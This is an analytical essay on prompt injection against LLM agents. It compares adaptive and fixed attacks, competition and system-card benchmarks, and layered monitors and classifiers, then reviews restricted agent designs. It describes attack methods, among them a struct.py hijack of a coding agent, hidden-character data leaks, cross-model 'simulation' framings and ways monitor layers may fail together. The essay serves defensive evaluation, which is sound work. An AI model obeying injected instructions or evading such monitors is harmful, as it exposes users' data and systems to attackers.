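A fixed set of attacks can also make a partly effective defence look stronger than it is, because its developers know the attacks in advance. In *Adaptive Attacks Break Defenses Against Indirect Prompt Injection Attacks on LLM Agents*, Zhan, Fang and colleagues used adaptive attacks to bypass all eight defences they tested, with success rates above 50%. But some reported gaps between fixed and adaptive attacks are probably too large. *Defending against Adaptive Prompt Injection Attacks via Reasoning-enabled Task Alignment* (2026) reports adaptive success of up to 50%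 against defences with low fixed-attack rates, but the fixed attacks covered 420 cases and the adaptive ones only a subset of 40 vulnerable cases.

*Adaptive Adversaries* (Jain, Hartmann and Li, 2026) avoided that problem by scoring the same contests after different numbers of rounds. In each contest, one language model attacks another for up to 15 rounds. The attacker remembers its earlier attempts and the replies, while the defender starts each round afresh. Three models played both roles, and each pairing ran five times in each of 21 scenarios, for a total of 945 contests.

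| Defending model | Broken in round 1 | Broken within 15 rounds |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.6 | 0.0% | 7.9% |
| GPT-5.4 | 0.0% | 9.5% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 1.0% | 16.8% |

The abstract on the ICML 2026 conference page gives slightly higher figures for the full contests, 8.3% to 19.0%.

More rounds also give the attacker more tries, so these figures alone don't show that it learned anything. To test for learning, Jain and colleagues compared attackers with and without a memory of their earlier attempts, on three scenarios and with 15 tries each. The attacker with a memory won 13 of 36 contests, and the one without won none. Most of the gain in these scenarios therefore came from learning, and the formula for independent attempts would not have predicted that gain.

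Part of the gap between the first round and the fifteenth is built in, because Jain and colleagues revised their scenarios during development to allow attacks to emerge over several rounds. This affects the comparison of memories less, since both attackers faced the same scenarios. The defenders also had no real tools, and the benchmark checked the structured answers they produced, such as a score or a decision.

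Averages also hid large differences between tasks, so an attacker who can choose the task can succeed more often than average. In a scenario about protecting a password, the attackers broke Opus in 30 of 60 follow-up contests, GPT-5.4 in 6 and Gemini in 3. In another, about a forged change to a reviewer's score, they broke Gemini 26 times, GPT-5.4 once and Opus never.

Developers could run adaptive tests of their own, but their failure to break a defence is weak evidence that nobody can. In *AutoDojo* (2026), Ma, Li and colleagues cite a precedent from image recognition, where a team in 2020 broke thirteen defences whose developers had already tested them against adaptive attacks. Nasr and colleagues accept that their own methods have the same limit, since failing to break a defence doesn't prove it secure.

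### A public competition with 272,000 attempts

The attacks on the twelve defences mostly targeted models from 2025 or earlier with a defence added. In *How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?*, Dziemian, Lin and colleagues (2026) tested 13 leading models by themselves, in the contest from which CAISI drew its findings. Over three weeks, 464 participants made about 272,000 attempts in 41 scenarios and succeeded 8,648 times. An attempt counted as a success only if it caused the harmful action and, in nearly every scenario, left no sign of it in the agent's final reply to the user.

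Attacks succeeded least often against Claude Opus 4.5, in 0.5% of attempts. The rates for two other Claude models, Sonnet 4.5 and Haiku 4.5, were 1.0% and 1.3%. Kimi K2's rate was 4.8% and Gemini 2.5 Pro's was 8.5%. Because of the concealment rule, these rates exclude many hijackings that the agent revealed. Gemini 2.5 Pro carried out the harmful action in about 16% of attempts, nearly twice its official rate.

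The results look worse when counted by scenario. Participants broke Opus 4.5 in 13 of the 37 scenarios included in the results, and Gemini 2.5 Pro in all 37. Successful attacks on each model continued at a roughly constant rate until the contest closed, so participants had not run out of ideas.

Dziemian and colleagues then ran 2,679 successful attacks against every model. The attacks that had beaten Opus 4.5 worked 44% to 81% of the time on the others. None of the attacks that had beaten Qwen3 VL, one of the weakest models, worked on Opus 4.5. Across the whole sample, attacks succeeded 53% of the time against Qwen3 VL and 2.5% against Opus 4.5. An attack that beats a strong model is therefore likely to work on many others, but an attacker can't count on attacks developed against a weak model to work on a stronger one.

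Some attacks also worked across tasks. One participant wrote 63 nearly identical attacks, all presenting the situation as a simulation. Together, they succeeded in 21 of the 41 scenarios and on nine models.

Participants saw the whole conversation before the injection point and knew which action they had to cause. The organisers also asked vendors to turn off external filters. Because of these conditions, Dziemian and colleagues call their rates an upper bound on vulnerability in a single turn. That description is fair given the access participants had, but the rates average over beginners and experts, so a more skilled attacker could exceed them. Participants could also reuse attacks that had worked on one model against another, which may inflate the transfer figures.

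### Later models and deterministic gates

Nasr and colleagues showed that these twelve defences fail and that the evidence for them was weak. Neither result implies that every future model will fail. The search attack's success rate against GPT-5 Mini, the most resistant model in their search tests, was between 47% and 81%, depending on the defence. The researchers believe a larger budget would have broken it too, but they did not test this.

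Later models have become much harder to attack. *Scaling Adaptive Prompt Injection Attacks with Agent Swarms* (Kurakin, Karande and colleagues, 2026) reports that by autumn 2026, attacks carried over from the public competition succeeded less than 1% of the time against recent Gemini models and some Claude models. The same Google DeepMind researchers then built a stronger attacker, which uses teams of AI agents that search for injections, share notes and see one another's best candidates. It could reliably trick models that had looked robust on public tests. All the models became easier to trick as the attacker became more capable.

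The test measured obedience to injected instructions more than harm. The attacker's goal was always a harmless tool call unrelated to the user's task, such as logging health data during a request to book a tutor. A model that followed such an order might still refuse to send an attacker a password. Kurakin and colleagues reply that an attacker could combine steps that each look harmless to cause harm. They also switched off Google's protections around Gemini. Their results are good evidence that a low score may not hold up against the next generation of attackers, but they cannot show that training will never catch up with those attackers.

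None of the twelve defences was a deterministic gate on the agent's actions. Nasr and colleagues left out three designs that plan the agent's actions before it reads untrusted text, among them CaMeL, because the attack was "guaranteed to fail" in most of their scenarios. An injection cannot add a step to a plan that is already fixed. They also caution that such designs suit a limited set of tasks and noticeably reduce usefulness. So "twelve out of twelve" partly reflects which defences they chose to attack, and their results provide little evidence for or against a gate.

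Developers of gates can still make the same mistake of relying on fixed tests. In *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents*, Narisetty, Kore and colleagues (2026) warn that most headline results for gates come from fixed attacks. They tried an adaptive attack on Progent, which checks every tool call against explicit rules. Progent reduced the average success rate of standard attacks from 25.8% to 4.2%, and the adaptive attack succeeded only 2.6% of the time. They tested just one handwritten attack on a small open model, and say only that the result is consistent with gates being harder targets.

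Rewording an injected instruction won't change a fixed rule, so an attacker who adapts to a gate has to find a harmful action that the rules allow, or influence whoever writes them. In Progent, a language model can write the rules, so an attacker may be able to influence that model.

### Attackers with less access

A sceptic can object that real attackers rarely see a detector's confidence score or the agent's reasoning, and that sending 800 versions of an email to one victim would attract attention. A defence that fails after hundreds of well-informed attempts might still work in ordinary use.

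Ma and colleagues tested a weaker attacker. Its only feedback is how often its injections succeed, it has no information about the defence or the user's request, and it can make only a small number of attempts. PIGuard had blocked every fixed attack on an agent running GPT-4o mini, but this attacker raised the success rate to 28%. Five defences had kept the success rate of fixed attacks near zero on that agent, and only Progent also kept this attacker's rate near zero. Nasr and colleagues reached 71% against PIGuard with more feedback, so limiting the attacker's access may well help the defender, although the two studies also used different models and budgets.

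Adapting an attack to a defence takes little expertise when the defence's code is public. *Locks Tested Without Burglars*, a NeurIPS workshop paper, reports that coding assistants such as Claude Code read the code of three defences, including Data Sentinel and MELON, and wrote attacks that raised attack success rates by up to 50–60%.

Attackers can also practise on their own account with the same product, then send the victim only what worked. Jain and colleagues replayed successful sequences of attacks, which worked again in 67.2% of trials against the same model but only 11.8% against a different one. Practice therefore helps most when the attacker knows which model the victim uses, and an update to that model may stop the attack from working. Once an attack works, posting it on many web pages or in many product reviews takes little more effort than posting it once.

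A widely posted payload will reach agents handling all sorts of requests, and the request strongly affects whether the attack succeeds. Ma and colleagues found that attacks succeeded much more often when the user told the agent to do whatever the content said, without naming an action. Attacks succeeded less often when the user specified the action, even if the agent had to look up the details. That fits OpenAI's advice to avoid open-ended requests.

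## Claude Opus 5 and the case for measured robustness

A guarantee usually makes an agent less useful, so a developer may reasonably ask whether a robust enough model makes the guarantee unnecessary. The best evidence that it does is Claude Opus 5, which Anthropic released in July 2026. The model's *System Card* (Anthropic, 2026) reports injection results in several settings. In one test, a single attempt succeeded 0.2% of the time. In another, no attack succeeded once Anthropic switched on its strongest safeguards.

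### Known attacks in 28 scenarios

Claude models had saturated Anthropic's previous external benchmark, so the company now reports results on the Indirect Prompt Injection benchmark, built with the security firm Gray Swan, the UK AI Security Institute, CAISI and other model developers. It follows the public competition that Dziemian and colleagues described and uses 28 new scenarios. Participants tried to make agents do something harmful and irreversible, such as leaking private data, destroying files or sending money. The final set has 1,130 attacks, chosen because they transferred well between target models.

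The last column below is a calculation from the one-attempt rates, using the formula for repeated independent attempts.

| Model | One attempt | Fifteen attempts | Fifteen attempts, if independent |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 5 | 0.2% | 2.0% | 3.0% |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 0.5% | 5.5% | 7.2% |
| GPT-5.6 Sol | 3.1% | 20.0% | 37.6% |

A single attempt against GPT-5.6 Sol, then OpenAI's strongest model in that family, succeeded more often than fifteen attempts against Opus 5. The most robust model not made by Anthropic was Muse Spark, with an attack success rate of 16.5% within fifteen attempts. Anthropic tested its own models without additional safeguards. It tested the others through their public interfaces, which may include safeguards, so in that respect the comparison did not favour Claude.

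For all three models in the table, attacks succeeded less often over fifteen attempts than they would if the attempts were independent. Rounding can't explain this for Opus 5, because even a single-attempt rate of 0.15%, the lowest that rounds to 0.2%, would give 2.2% over fifteen attempts. Successes are probably concentrated in a few easy scenarios. Opus 5's 2.0% average over 28 scenarios could mean that attacks succeed within fifteen attempts about half the time in one scenario and never in the other 27.

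The bunching is easier to see over longer runs. The Decoder's *Claude Opus 4.5 resists prompt injections better than rivals* reports an earlier Gray Swan test in which attackers succeeded 4.7% of the time with one attempt, 33.6% with ten and 63% with a hundred. If the attempts had been independent, the rates would have been 38% with ten and 99% with a hundred. Repeated attempts therefore help an attacker less than the formula suggests when the target is hard.

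The benchmark is also limited by its fixed set of attacks, which participants wrote in early 2026, months before Opus 5 came out. The fifteen attempts do not adapt to the model's replies. The 2.0% therefore measures how well older attacks carry over to a newer model. This is useful because many real attackers will reuse what they find online, but a patient attacker who targets Opus 5 may do better.

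### Attackers who rehearse on the test

Anthropic's other tests use adaptive attackers. For coding and computer use, Anthropic used Shade, an automated attacker from Gray Swan that combines search, reinforcement learning and ideas from human red-teamers. Shade made 200 attempts in each scenario.

In the coding test, the attacker succeeded in 0.56% of its attempts on Opus 5 with extended thinking, a setting in which the model reasons at length before it acts. That is about 45 successes in 8,000 attempts, and they occurred in 13 of the 40 scenarios. An attacker with a single try had about one chance in 180, while an attacker who could send 200 versions got through in about a third of the scenarios. If every attempt had carried the same independent 0.56% chance, the attacker would have succeeded in about 27 scenarios, so here too the successes were clustered in certain scenarios.

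Shade had trained on these coding scenarios, but against earlier models, and its attacks were then transferred to Opus 5. The computer-use test, in which the agent sees and operates a screen as a person would, was tougher in this respect because the attacker optimised directly against the test cases. Attacks succeeded against Opus 5 in one of 14 scenarios, and in that scenario about 7.5% of attempts worked. With so few scenarios, the result is compatible, at 95% confidence, with a true failure rate of up to 30% of such scenarios.

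The improvement over earlier models is still hard to dismiss. In February 2026, VentureBeat reported Anthropic's results for injection attacks on Claude Opus 4.6 in a graphical interface. A single attempt succeeded 17.8% of the time, and by the 200th attempt the attacker had broken through in 78.6% of cases, or 57.1% with safeguards. The last two percentages match 11 and 8 scenarios out of 14, and the July test also used 14 scenarios. If Anthropic kept the same scenarios, the number broken fell from 11 to one in less than six months.

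The coding results show the risk of extrapolating from a good score. In VentureBeat's account of the February coding test, none of 200 attacks on Opus 4.6 succeeded. In the July results, Shade broke its successor, Opus 4.8, in 23 of 40 coding scenarios, with 7.03% of attempts succeeding. Either the later model was weaker or the later test was harder, and in both cases the February score was a poor guide to the July result.

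### Robustness does not simply follow capability

All rates below are for models with extended thinking and no additional safeguards. The Gray Swan column gives the chance of at least one success in fifteen attempts, and the other columns give the share of single attempts that succeeded.

| Model | Gray Swan | Coding | Computer use | Browser |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 5 | 2.0% | 0.56% | 0.54% | 3.70% |
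| Claude Mythos 5 | 2.6% | 0.45% | 0.82% | 29.7% |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 5.5% | 7.03% | 7.14% | 31.5% |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 5.9% | 0.31% | 2.25% | 0.93% |

Anthropic rates Mythos 5 as more capable than Opus 5 at exploiting software flaws and in biology. Yet attackers hijacked Mythos 5 in 29.7% of browser attempts, eight times the rate for Opus 5 and about 32 times the rate for Sonnet 5, which is weaker than either on most of Anthropic's capability tests. OpenAI may still be right to expect that a sufficiently intelligent model will resist manipulation, but in these tests attackers hijacked the more capable models more often.

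A model's robustness also depends on the setting. Sonnet 5 had the lowest attack success rate of the four models in the browser and the highest on the Gray Swan benchmark. With extended thinking, the rate against Opus 4.8 fell from 17.44% to 7.03% in coding but rose from 17.8% to 31.5% in the browser. Anthropic does not explain these reversals. A buyer who wants to know how a browser agent will behave should ask for browser results, since the other results would have been misleading about Mythos 5.

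### Auto mode and the zero in 129 scenarios

For the browser test, Anthropic built 129 web environments containing attacks by professional red-teamers. It kept them out of training, and ordinary code checked whether each injection had worked. The attacker had ten attempts in each environment. Without safeguards, 3.70% of attempts on Opus 5 succeeded, in 11 of the 129 environments. With a set of safeguards called auto mode, no attempts succeeded.

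Auto mode has two layers:

1. Probes inspect each tool result before the model acts on it, and flag text that looks like an injected instruction.
2. A classifier inspects each tool call that the model proposes, and blocks calls that look dangerous.

The classifier is a model-based gate, so it can approve a call that it should block. Anthropic argues that the two layers fail independently because the probe checks incoming data and the classifier checks outgoing actions, so an attack must defeat both. If each layer missed 10% of attacks and their misses were unrelated, only 1% would get past both. But checking different things does not make their misses independent. The probe may miss an injection written as a routine business request, and the classifier may then approve the routine-looking call that results.

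The zero is due more to auto mode than to Opus 5. Attacks succeeded against Mythos 5 in 71 of the 129 scenarios when it ran by itself, but in none with auto mode on. For Opus 4.8, the number fell from 81 to one. Probes alone achieved less in the other tests. In coding, they reduced the attack success rate against Opus 5 from 0.56% to 0.18%, but against Mythos 5 only from 0.45% to 0.41%, a difference that may well be chance. Anthropic did not test the browser agent with the classifier alone, so the classifier's share of the improvement is unknown. The injection results also don't include how often auto mode inconveniences users by blocking harmless calls.

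The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection* drew an optimistic conclusion from the zero. How much can a zero establish? Suppose that auto mode fails in a fraction *q* of all scenarios of this kind, and that the 129 are a random sample of them. The chance of seeing no failures is then (1 − *q*)^129. The largest *q* that would still produce a clean result at least 5% of the time solves

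(1 − *q*)^129 = 0.05, which gives *q* = 1 − 0.05^(1/129) ≈ 2.3%

So at 95% confidence, the result is compatible with auto mode failing in up to about one scenario in 43. The true rate may be far lower, but the test is too small to show whether it is.

The upper bound should be calculated from the 129 scenarios rather than the 1,290 attempts, because ten attempts in one scenario are less informative than single attempts in ten different scenarios. Without safeguards, the roughly 48 successful attempts fell in 11 scenarios, an average of more than four successes out of ten in each, while the other 118 scenarios had none. Once the first few attempts in a scenario have failed, the rest add little. Treating the result as zero successes in 1,290 independent attempts would give an upper bound of 0.23%, which is too low. Running the same 129 scenarios on Sonnet 5 and Mythos 5 does not enlarge the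 sample of scenarios either.

Even the 2.3% holds only if future attacks resemble the tested ones. Anthropic used adaptive attackers in this part of its testing. It considers the conditions generous to them, because real attackers don't know the exact deployment and risk being detected when they keep trying. That is a fair point about Opus 5 by itself, but Anthropic does not say that the red-teamers revised their attacks against auto mode, the setup that produced the zero. For earlier models, Anthropic had also published results from a live bug bounty in which outsiders directly attacked its latest model at the time, but the bounty for Opus 5 was still being set up in July.

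In August 2026, Four Signals' *Prompt Injection in Claude Code Opus 5 Auto Mode* (2026) described an attack on Anthropic's coding agent, Claude Code, that the security blog Embrace The Red had found. Willison also wrote about it. According to SnipVote's *Breaking Claude Code Opus 5 Auto Mode* (2026), a digest of AI-written summaries of such posts, the attack reportedly worked 80% of the time. It used a zip archive to get Python to load a malicious file called struct.py. A program that imports Python's standard struct module can end up running a file of that name from its own folder instead. A classifier that checks the command may detect only an ordinary Python program, because the malicious code is in a file that the command doesn't mention.

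The digest does not give the number of trials, so the 80% is a rough figure. The attack was also on a coding agent, not a browser. It doesn't contradict the result in the 129 browser scenarios, but the upper bound from those scenarios cannot cover an attack like this, which was not drawn from the same pool.

### Results for newer models

Anthropic has since improved on Opus 5 with Claude Opus 5.5, whose *System Card* (2026), released in September, reports similar or better performance on every injection test. *Anthropic's new budget model gets much better at ignoring hidden commands* (Pogorelec, 2026), published in October, describes a similar advance in the small, cheap Claude Haiku 5.5.

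Opus 5.5 is more likely than earlier models to follow malicious instructions in text that users paste into their own messages. Digital Matters' *Claude Opus 5.5 Prompt Injection* (2026) reports this alongside Anthropic's launch-page claim that Opus 5.5 ties with Claude Fable 5.1 for the lowest attack success rate on a Gray Swan benchmark. A pasted email is labelled as user input rather than a tool result, so the model has only the wording to tell it whether an instruction came from the user. Anthropic says it has mitigations for this. People often paste emails into chats, and an organisation that chose Opus 5.5 for its benchmark rank could miss the weakness.

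Cross (2026), in *GPT-6 Sol Scores 97.13% on Indirect Injection Defense*, reports that GPT-6 Sol resisted 99.99% of direct attacks in OpenAI's October tests, but 97.13% of indirect ones, which arrive through outside content. TechRepublic's *OpenAI’s GPT-5.6 Tests Show Prompt-Injection Gains and Agent Risks* (2026) had described the same pattern in the previous generation. For an agent that reads strangers' email, the indirect rate is the relevant one. OpenAI measured these rates using its own attacks, so they can't be ranked against Anthropic's.

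Newer models do not always resist manipulation better. Mowshowitz (2026), in *GPT-6.2 Astra and Sol*, notes that OpenAI saw regressions in jailbreak resistance in its November models and adjusted their refusal boundaries in response. These regressions provide little direct evidence about injection, but they are a reason to test each new release.

PromptArmor's recent *FrontierBreach* test puts models from several companies through the same attacks. It takes realistic office tasks, such as analysing a bond portfolio, and adds attacks modelled on ones PromptArmor's researchers have found in real products. The attacks are designed to make the agent leak data, run ransomware or tamper with systems. The rates below are for five attempts, with PromptArmor's 95% margins.

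| Model | Attack success rate |
|---|---|
| Gemini 4 Carbon | 2.4% ± 2.2 |
| Gemini 4 Argon | 4.3% ± 2.9 |
| GPT-6 Astra | 7.6% ± 3.8 |
| Claude Fable 5.2 | 10.0% ± 4.2 |
| Claude Opus 5 | 10.0% ± 4.2 |
| GPT-5.6 Sol | 33.3% ± 6.7 |

On PromptArmor's benchmark, Opus 5 did five times worse with five attempts than it did on the Gray Swan benchmark with fifteen, and both Gemini 4 models did better than it. PromptArmor sells AI security and advertises its benchmark's high attack success rates against leading models, so it has an incentive to choose attacks that work, as criminals do. Opus 5 is much harder to hijack than GPT-5.6 Sol on both benchmarks, but its failure rate differs between them, and the results don't show which benchmark is closer to the attacks that a given company will face.

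### Whether a low rate is enough

Boris Cherny, who leads Claude Code at Anthropic, found the injection results more exciting than any of the capability scores. Willison (2026) reposted his remark that Opus 5 is "very hard to prompt inject successfully". ClawSouls' *The most exciting line was buried in a system card* quotes a further claim that combining a well-aligned model with probes and auto mode brings the injection success rate down to "~0".

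In *Anthropic's Opus 5 Is Better at Resisting Prompt Injection*, the well-known security writer Bruce Schneier (2026) accepts that the model has improved but doesn't think this settles the matter. He thinks that preventing prompt injection is impossible in general, but that developers are getting much better at blocking it in specific cases. The evidence fits his claim about specific cases well, but existing proofs don't establish that general prevention is impossible. A reader of the blog also objected that a paper offered in support was about jailbreaks, not injections. Schneier could make the same argument with the safer claim that nobody knows how to prevent prompt injection in general.

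Willison posted Cherny's remark without comment in July, but he has long held that stopping 95% of attacks is a failing grade in web application security. Opus 5 stops 99.8% of single attempts on the Gray Swan benchmark, but that doesn't answer his objection, because real attackers don't choose their attacks at random. In the browser test without safeguards, an attacker choosing at random succeeded 3.70% of the time, while one who knew which 11 scenarios were vulnerable would have succeeded about 43% of the time.

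The web comparison is also less apt because general-purpose agents have no fix as easy and complete as parameterised queries. Those queries stop the whole class of SQL injection attacks with little effort, which makes a 95% filter a poor choice. Anyone who rejects a low rate of successful attacks on an agent has to either accept restrictions on the agent or not use one.

Defenders of measured robustness can add that ordinary security routinely manages failure rates. Spam filters let some fraud through, and banks budget for stolen cards. PYMNTS's *Anthropic Pushes Back as Hackers Press AI Weak Spots* describes AI companies doing much the same, with preventive controls, detection and measures to limit damage. It also treats a 1% attack success rate as a meaningful risk.

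This reply is right that a nonzero rate can be acceptable, but the examples work for particular reasons. A thief guessing a random six-digit security code that locks after three wrong guesses has three chances in a million, and cleverness doesn't improve those odds. A better attacker can raise the success rate of injection, as the attack on auto mode did. Card fraud is a closer comparison, since criminals do adapt, but a bank can tolerate the fraud rate because it controls the size of each loss. It can cap a transaction, spot an unusual pattern and refund the customer afterwards.

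Losses from injection may also arrive together. Suppose 10,000 people run the same agent, and each has a 0.2% chance of a hijacking this month. If the failures are independent, about 20 people will be affected, which the company can plan for. If instead there is a 0.2% chance that someone finds a payload that works on every copy, all 10,000 people will be affected in one month out of 500, on average, and nobody in the others. The expected number of victims is the same, but an insurer could price the first risk easily and would be far more wary of the second. Real agents fall somewhere between the two because users have different tasks and settings, but the bunching in Anthropic's results suggests that independence should not be the default assumption.

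Whether a low rate is enough depends less on the rate than on how much harm one successful attack can do. A low rate is enough for an agent that summarises public web pages while logged out of the user's accounts, where the worst likely result is a misleading summary. It is probably enough for a coding agent that works in an isolated container with no passwords or keys, has restricted network access and hands its work to a person for review. In such cases, moving from Opus 4.8 to Opus 5 helps because it means fewer wasted runs and fewer bad outputs to catch. The same is true when losses are firmly capped, as with an agent that can issue small refunds up to a daily total.

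A low rate of successful injections is not enough when a single success could do severe damage that is hard to reverse. This applies to an agent that can make large payments, delete the only copy of a file, or read confidential records and send messages outside the company. If a company's agents meet 50,000 injected messages a year and 0.2% succeed, the agents will be hijacked 100 times. If each hijacking costs $50 in staff time, the total is $5,000, which many companies would accept. But if any one hijacking could expose the customer database, a model that cut the success rate to a tenth would still be hijacked ten times a year.

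An email assistant that can read a whole mailbox and write to anyone belongs in this second group, even though it is one of the products people most want. A better model makes each attack on it less likely to succeed. Limiting whom the assistant can write to, or what it can read before it writes, reduces what an attacker gains from a successful attack.

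## Six restricted designs and what each leaves open

Beurer-Kellner and colleagues offer a rule for building agents with narrower jobs, rather than a guarantee for every agent. Once an agent has taken in untrusted content, that content must not be able to trigger a consequential action, meaning one that harms the system or its surroundings. At a minimum, the agent must not be able to call a tool that could leak secrets or damage data. Its output must also be harmless. A summary can contain a link with private data in its address, which leaks the data when the user clicks, and a reply can contain instructions that mislead the next agent that reads it.

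The rule assumes that the injection works. Willison, who coined the term "prompt injection", writes in a commentary on the paper by Beurer-Kellner and colleagues that designers should assume anyone who gets text in front of the model controls everything it produces next, including its tool calls. The attacker's wording then makes no difference, so the adaptive attacks that defeat detectors have no advantage here.

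The six designs differ mainly in how much a model may read before it commits to its actions.

### Committing to actions before reading

The strictest design is the action selector. The model reads the user's request and picks from a list of actions that a programmer wrote in advance, such as fetching a link to the customer's last order. Some actions may be templates, such as a database query with a blank for the product name. The model never sees what an action returns, so an instruction hidden in a file or web page cannot reach it. An attacker who persuades a customer to paste text into the request can still choose among the listed actions, so every action has to be safe whoever asks for it.

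The action selector can't do anything that requires reading. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues note that, in an assistant that organises a user's files, this design shifts most of the work to whoever writes the commands. It also loses most of the model's ability to find "all tax-related PDF files" from a loose description.

Plan-then-execute is more permissive. The model reads the request and writes a fixed list of tool calls, and only then does the program run them. The model may read the results and use them to fill in blanks in later calls, but it cannot add a call. For the request "send today's schedule to my boss John Doe", the plan has two steps:

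1. Read today's calendar.
2. Send an email to john.doe@company.com, with the body still blank.

Suppose an outsider's calendar invitation contains an instruction to forward the user's recent mail to a second address. The agent cannot do this, because its plan has one step that sends mail and none that reads it. The injection also cannot replace John Doe's address, because the model wrote that address before it read the calendar. But the model writes the body of the email after reading the invitation, so the attacker can dictate the whole message. The message could give a false schedule, ask the boss in the user's name to approve a payment, or carry another injection aimed at the boss's own assistant.

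This protection depends on how much the plan fixes. If a file assistant's plan fixes only the commands for finding and moving files, an injection can make it find sensitive files and put them on a public network drive. In *Taming AI Agents with seL4*, Alhindi (2026) tested a limit on functions alone, using 249 attack cases from AgentDojo's banking and Slack tasks. Attacks succeeded in 48% of runs when the agent could call every function, and in 7% when the operating system's kernel blocked every function the user's task didn't need. With this limit, the agent completed 58% of ordinary tasks instead of 68%, a difference small enough to be chance.

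Every attack that still succeeded used only functions the task needed. About half used the function for sending money, which the agent needed to pay a bill, and named the attacker as the recipient. If the user names the payee, a plan that also fixed the recipient would stop these attacks. But when the user says "pay the bill in my inbox", the account number has to come from the bill. Alhindi took the permitted functions from AgentDojo's own solutions, and points out that someone granting functions before knowing the task would probably grant more.

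Beurer-Kellner and colleagues think an email assistant loses little usefulness by following a good plan, because untrusted text should rarely decide which actions it takes or in what order. An attacker can still steal data through one of their example requests, in which the user asks the assistant to answer an email by looking through recent mail for whatever its sender wants to know. The plan is to read the email, search the mailbox and reply to the sender. If the sender is the attacker, a hidden instruction in the email can make the assistant search for other sensitive information and encode it in the reply using characters that don't show on screen. The assistant makes only the planned calls and replies to the person the user chose, and even a careful user who checks the draft may miss the hidden data.

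### Reading each document separately

The map-reduce design is named after a method for splitting a computation across many machines. The system makes a separate model call for each document. These calls have no harmful tools, and each returns a short answer in a fixed format. Ordinary code then either combines the answers itself or checks their format and passes them to a model with tools, which combines them.

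For example, a user asks an agent to find this month's invoices and email them to the accounting department. Each model call reads one file and gives a yes-or-no answer on whether it is one of those invoices. An injection in a file can get that file classed as an invoice, but the attacker could have done the same by writing a fake invoice. The injection cannot change how the agent treats other files or where it sends them. These limits hold only if the final step attaches the files without reading them. A model that read them to write a covering summary would be exposed to the injection.

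This design suits questions with short answers that someone can specify in advance. A tool that summarises product reviews can count how many reviewers found a toaster easy to use, but it will miss a fault that nobody thought to include as a category. The design also cannot handle tasks that require reading several documents together.

Designers can combine it with a fixed plan. In the schedule example, formatting each calendar entry in a separate call would confine the outsider's invitation to its own line of the email, so it could no longer change the times of other meetings.

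### Separating the tools from the untrusted text

Willison proposed the dual model design in 2023. A privileged model reads the user's request, plans the work and holds the tools. A quarantined model reads untrusted content and has no tools. Ordinary code, called the orchestrator, passes values between them. If the user wants to write to an event's organiser, whose address is on a web page, the exchange runs like this:

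1. The privileged model asks the quarantined model to find the address.
2. The orchestrator stores the answer and gives the privileged model only a label for it, such as $VAR.
3. The privileged model calls the email tool with $VAR as the recipient.
4. The orchestrator replaces the label with the stored address as it makes the call.

The privileged model never reads the page, so nothing on the page can make it call a tool. But the page's author controls the value behind the label and can supply a different address. The quarantined model can also leak any private material it receives. In an example by Dongol, an injection makes it quote the user's notes in a reply that the plan then sends.

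The main drawback is that the privileged model cannot base decisions on text it never sees. Jacob, Alghamdi and colleagues (2025) relax this restriction in *Preventing Prompt Injection with Type-Directed Privilege Separation*. Their quarantined model may pass the privileged model numbers, true-or-false values and choices from a predefined list, but not free text.

One test of this defence used an agent that arranges meetings by email. The quarantined model reads the other person's messages and returns only the time slots they propose. Without the defence, an injection made the agent leak private calendar details in 63% of email threads. With it, the agent leaked nothing and arranged meetings as successfully as before (91% against 90%). A shopping agent that reduced each product review to two scores out of ten also kept its success rate. Each test used a single fixed injection, so the 63%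 doesn't show what a determined attacker could achieve. The absence of leaks with the defence is a more reliable result, because the attacker's wording never reaches the model that can use the tools.

However, an attacker can still supply a false number, and Jacob and colleagues concede that such misinformation can mislead the agent. Their scheduling agent also copies a free-text description of the meeting into the user's calendar without the privileged model reading it. That description could contain an injection for the next agent that reads the calendar. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues' rule is meant to exclude this kind of downstream risk.

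Code-then-execute takes the dual model further by having the privileged model write a complete program. For the schedule, it might write:

```
entries = calendar.read(today)
body = quarantined_model("format these entries", entries)
email.write(body, "john.doe@company.com")
```

Much as with the fixed plan, the injection can change the email's body but not its recipient, and it cannot add a call. A program can also express tasks that a simple list cannot, such as "Notify my regular collaborators that I will be on vacation next week", which needs a loop that sends one email to each of an unknown number of people. But if the program chooses its next step by testing an untrusted value, the attacker can influence that choice, though only among steps already in the program. Debenedetti and colleagues' CaMeL, the fullest system of this kind, also tracks where each value came from.

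The agent loses the ability to revise its approach after seeing a result. In one case study, an agent answers questions from a company's databases, but generated code processes the query results to keep injections in the data away from the model. The agent can still produce a chart of sales, but it can't notice that the figures are incomplete and write a better query.

### Removing the user's prompt

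Context minimisation protects against injections in the user's own message. The system uses the message to choose an action, then removes it from the context before the model writes a reply. Suppose a customer asks a car dealer's chatbot for a quote and adds an instruction to offer a large discount. The model turns the message into a database query for current offers, then writes its reply from the results without seeing the message again.

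The customer can still influence the query, and anything derived from the customer's message can carry an injection if it stays in the context. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues describe a medical chatbot that summarises a patient's symptoms, consults a database or a doctor, and explains the diagnosis. Removing the patient's message still leaves the summary, which the patient may have manipulated. Removing the summary too removes that risk, but the explanation then can't respond to anything the patient said.

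This design also matters for strangers' text that users paste into their own messages, which remains a weak point even for Claude Opus 5.5.

### The software engineering agent

Of Beurer-Kellner and colleagues' ten case studies, the coding assistant is the closest to a general-purpose agent. It reads online documentation, installs software packages and publishes code. A hostile web page could make it write insecure code, import a malicious package or leak secrets in the code it publishes.

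Asking the user to approve sensitive actions is tedious and can miss the attack. Instead of downloading a malicious package itself, the agent can add a line that imports it and leave the user to install it when the program fails to compile. Allowing only trusted sources of documentation and code is safer but makes the agent much less useful.

The safest option they consider is a dual model with a strict format. A quarantined model reads a library's documentation and converts it into a description of the library's functions, in a format that might, for instance, limit method names to 30 characters. The coding agent sees only this description, without the explanations and examples that programmers often need to use a library correctly.

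Even this doesn't guarantee safety. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues say only that an injection is "unlikely" to survive a strict enough format. Willison wonders whether an attacker could use a method name such as run_rm_dash_rf_for_compliance, which alludes to a command that deletes files. The name is 29 characters long, so it fits the limit. Current models may well ignore it, but a length limit cannot ensure that text isn't an instruction.

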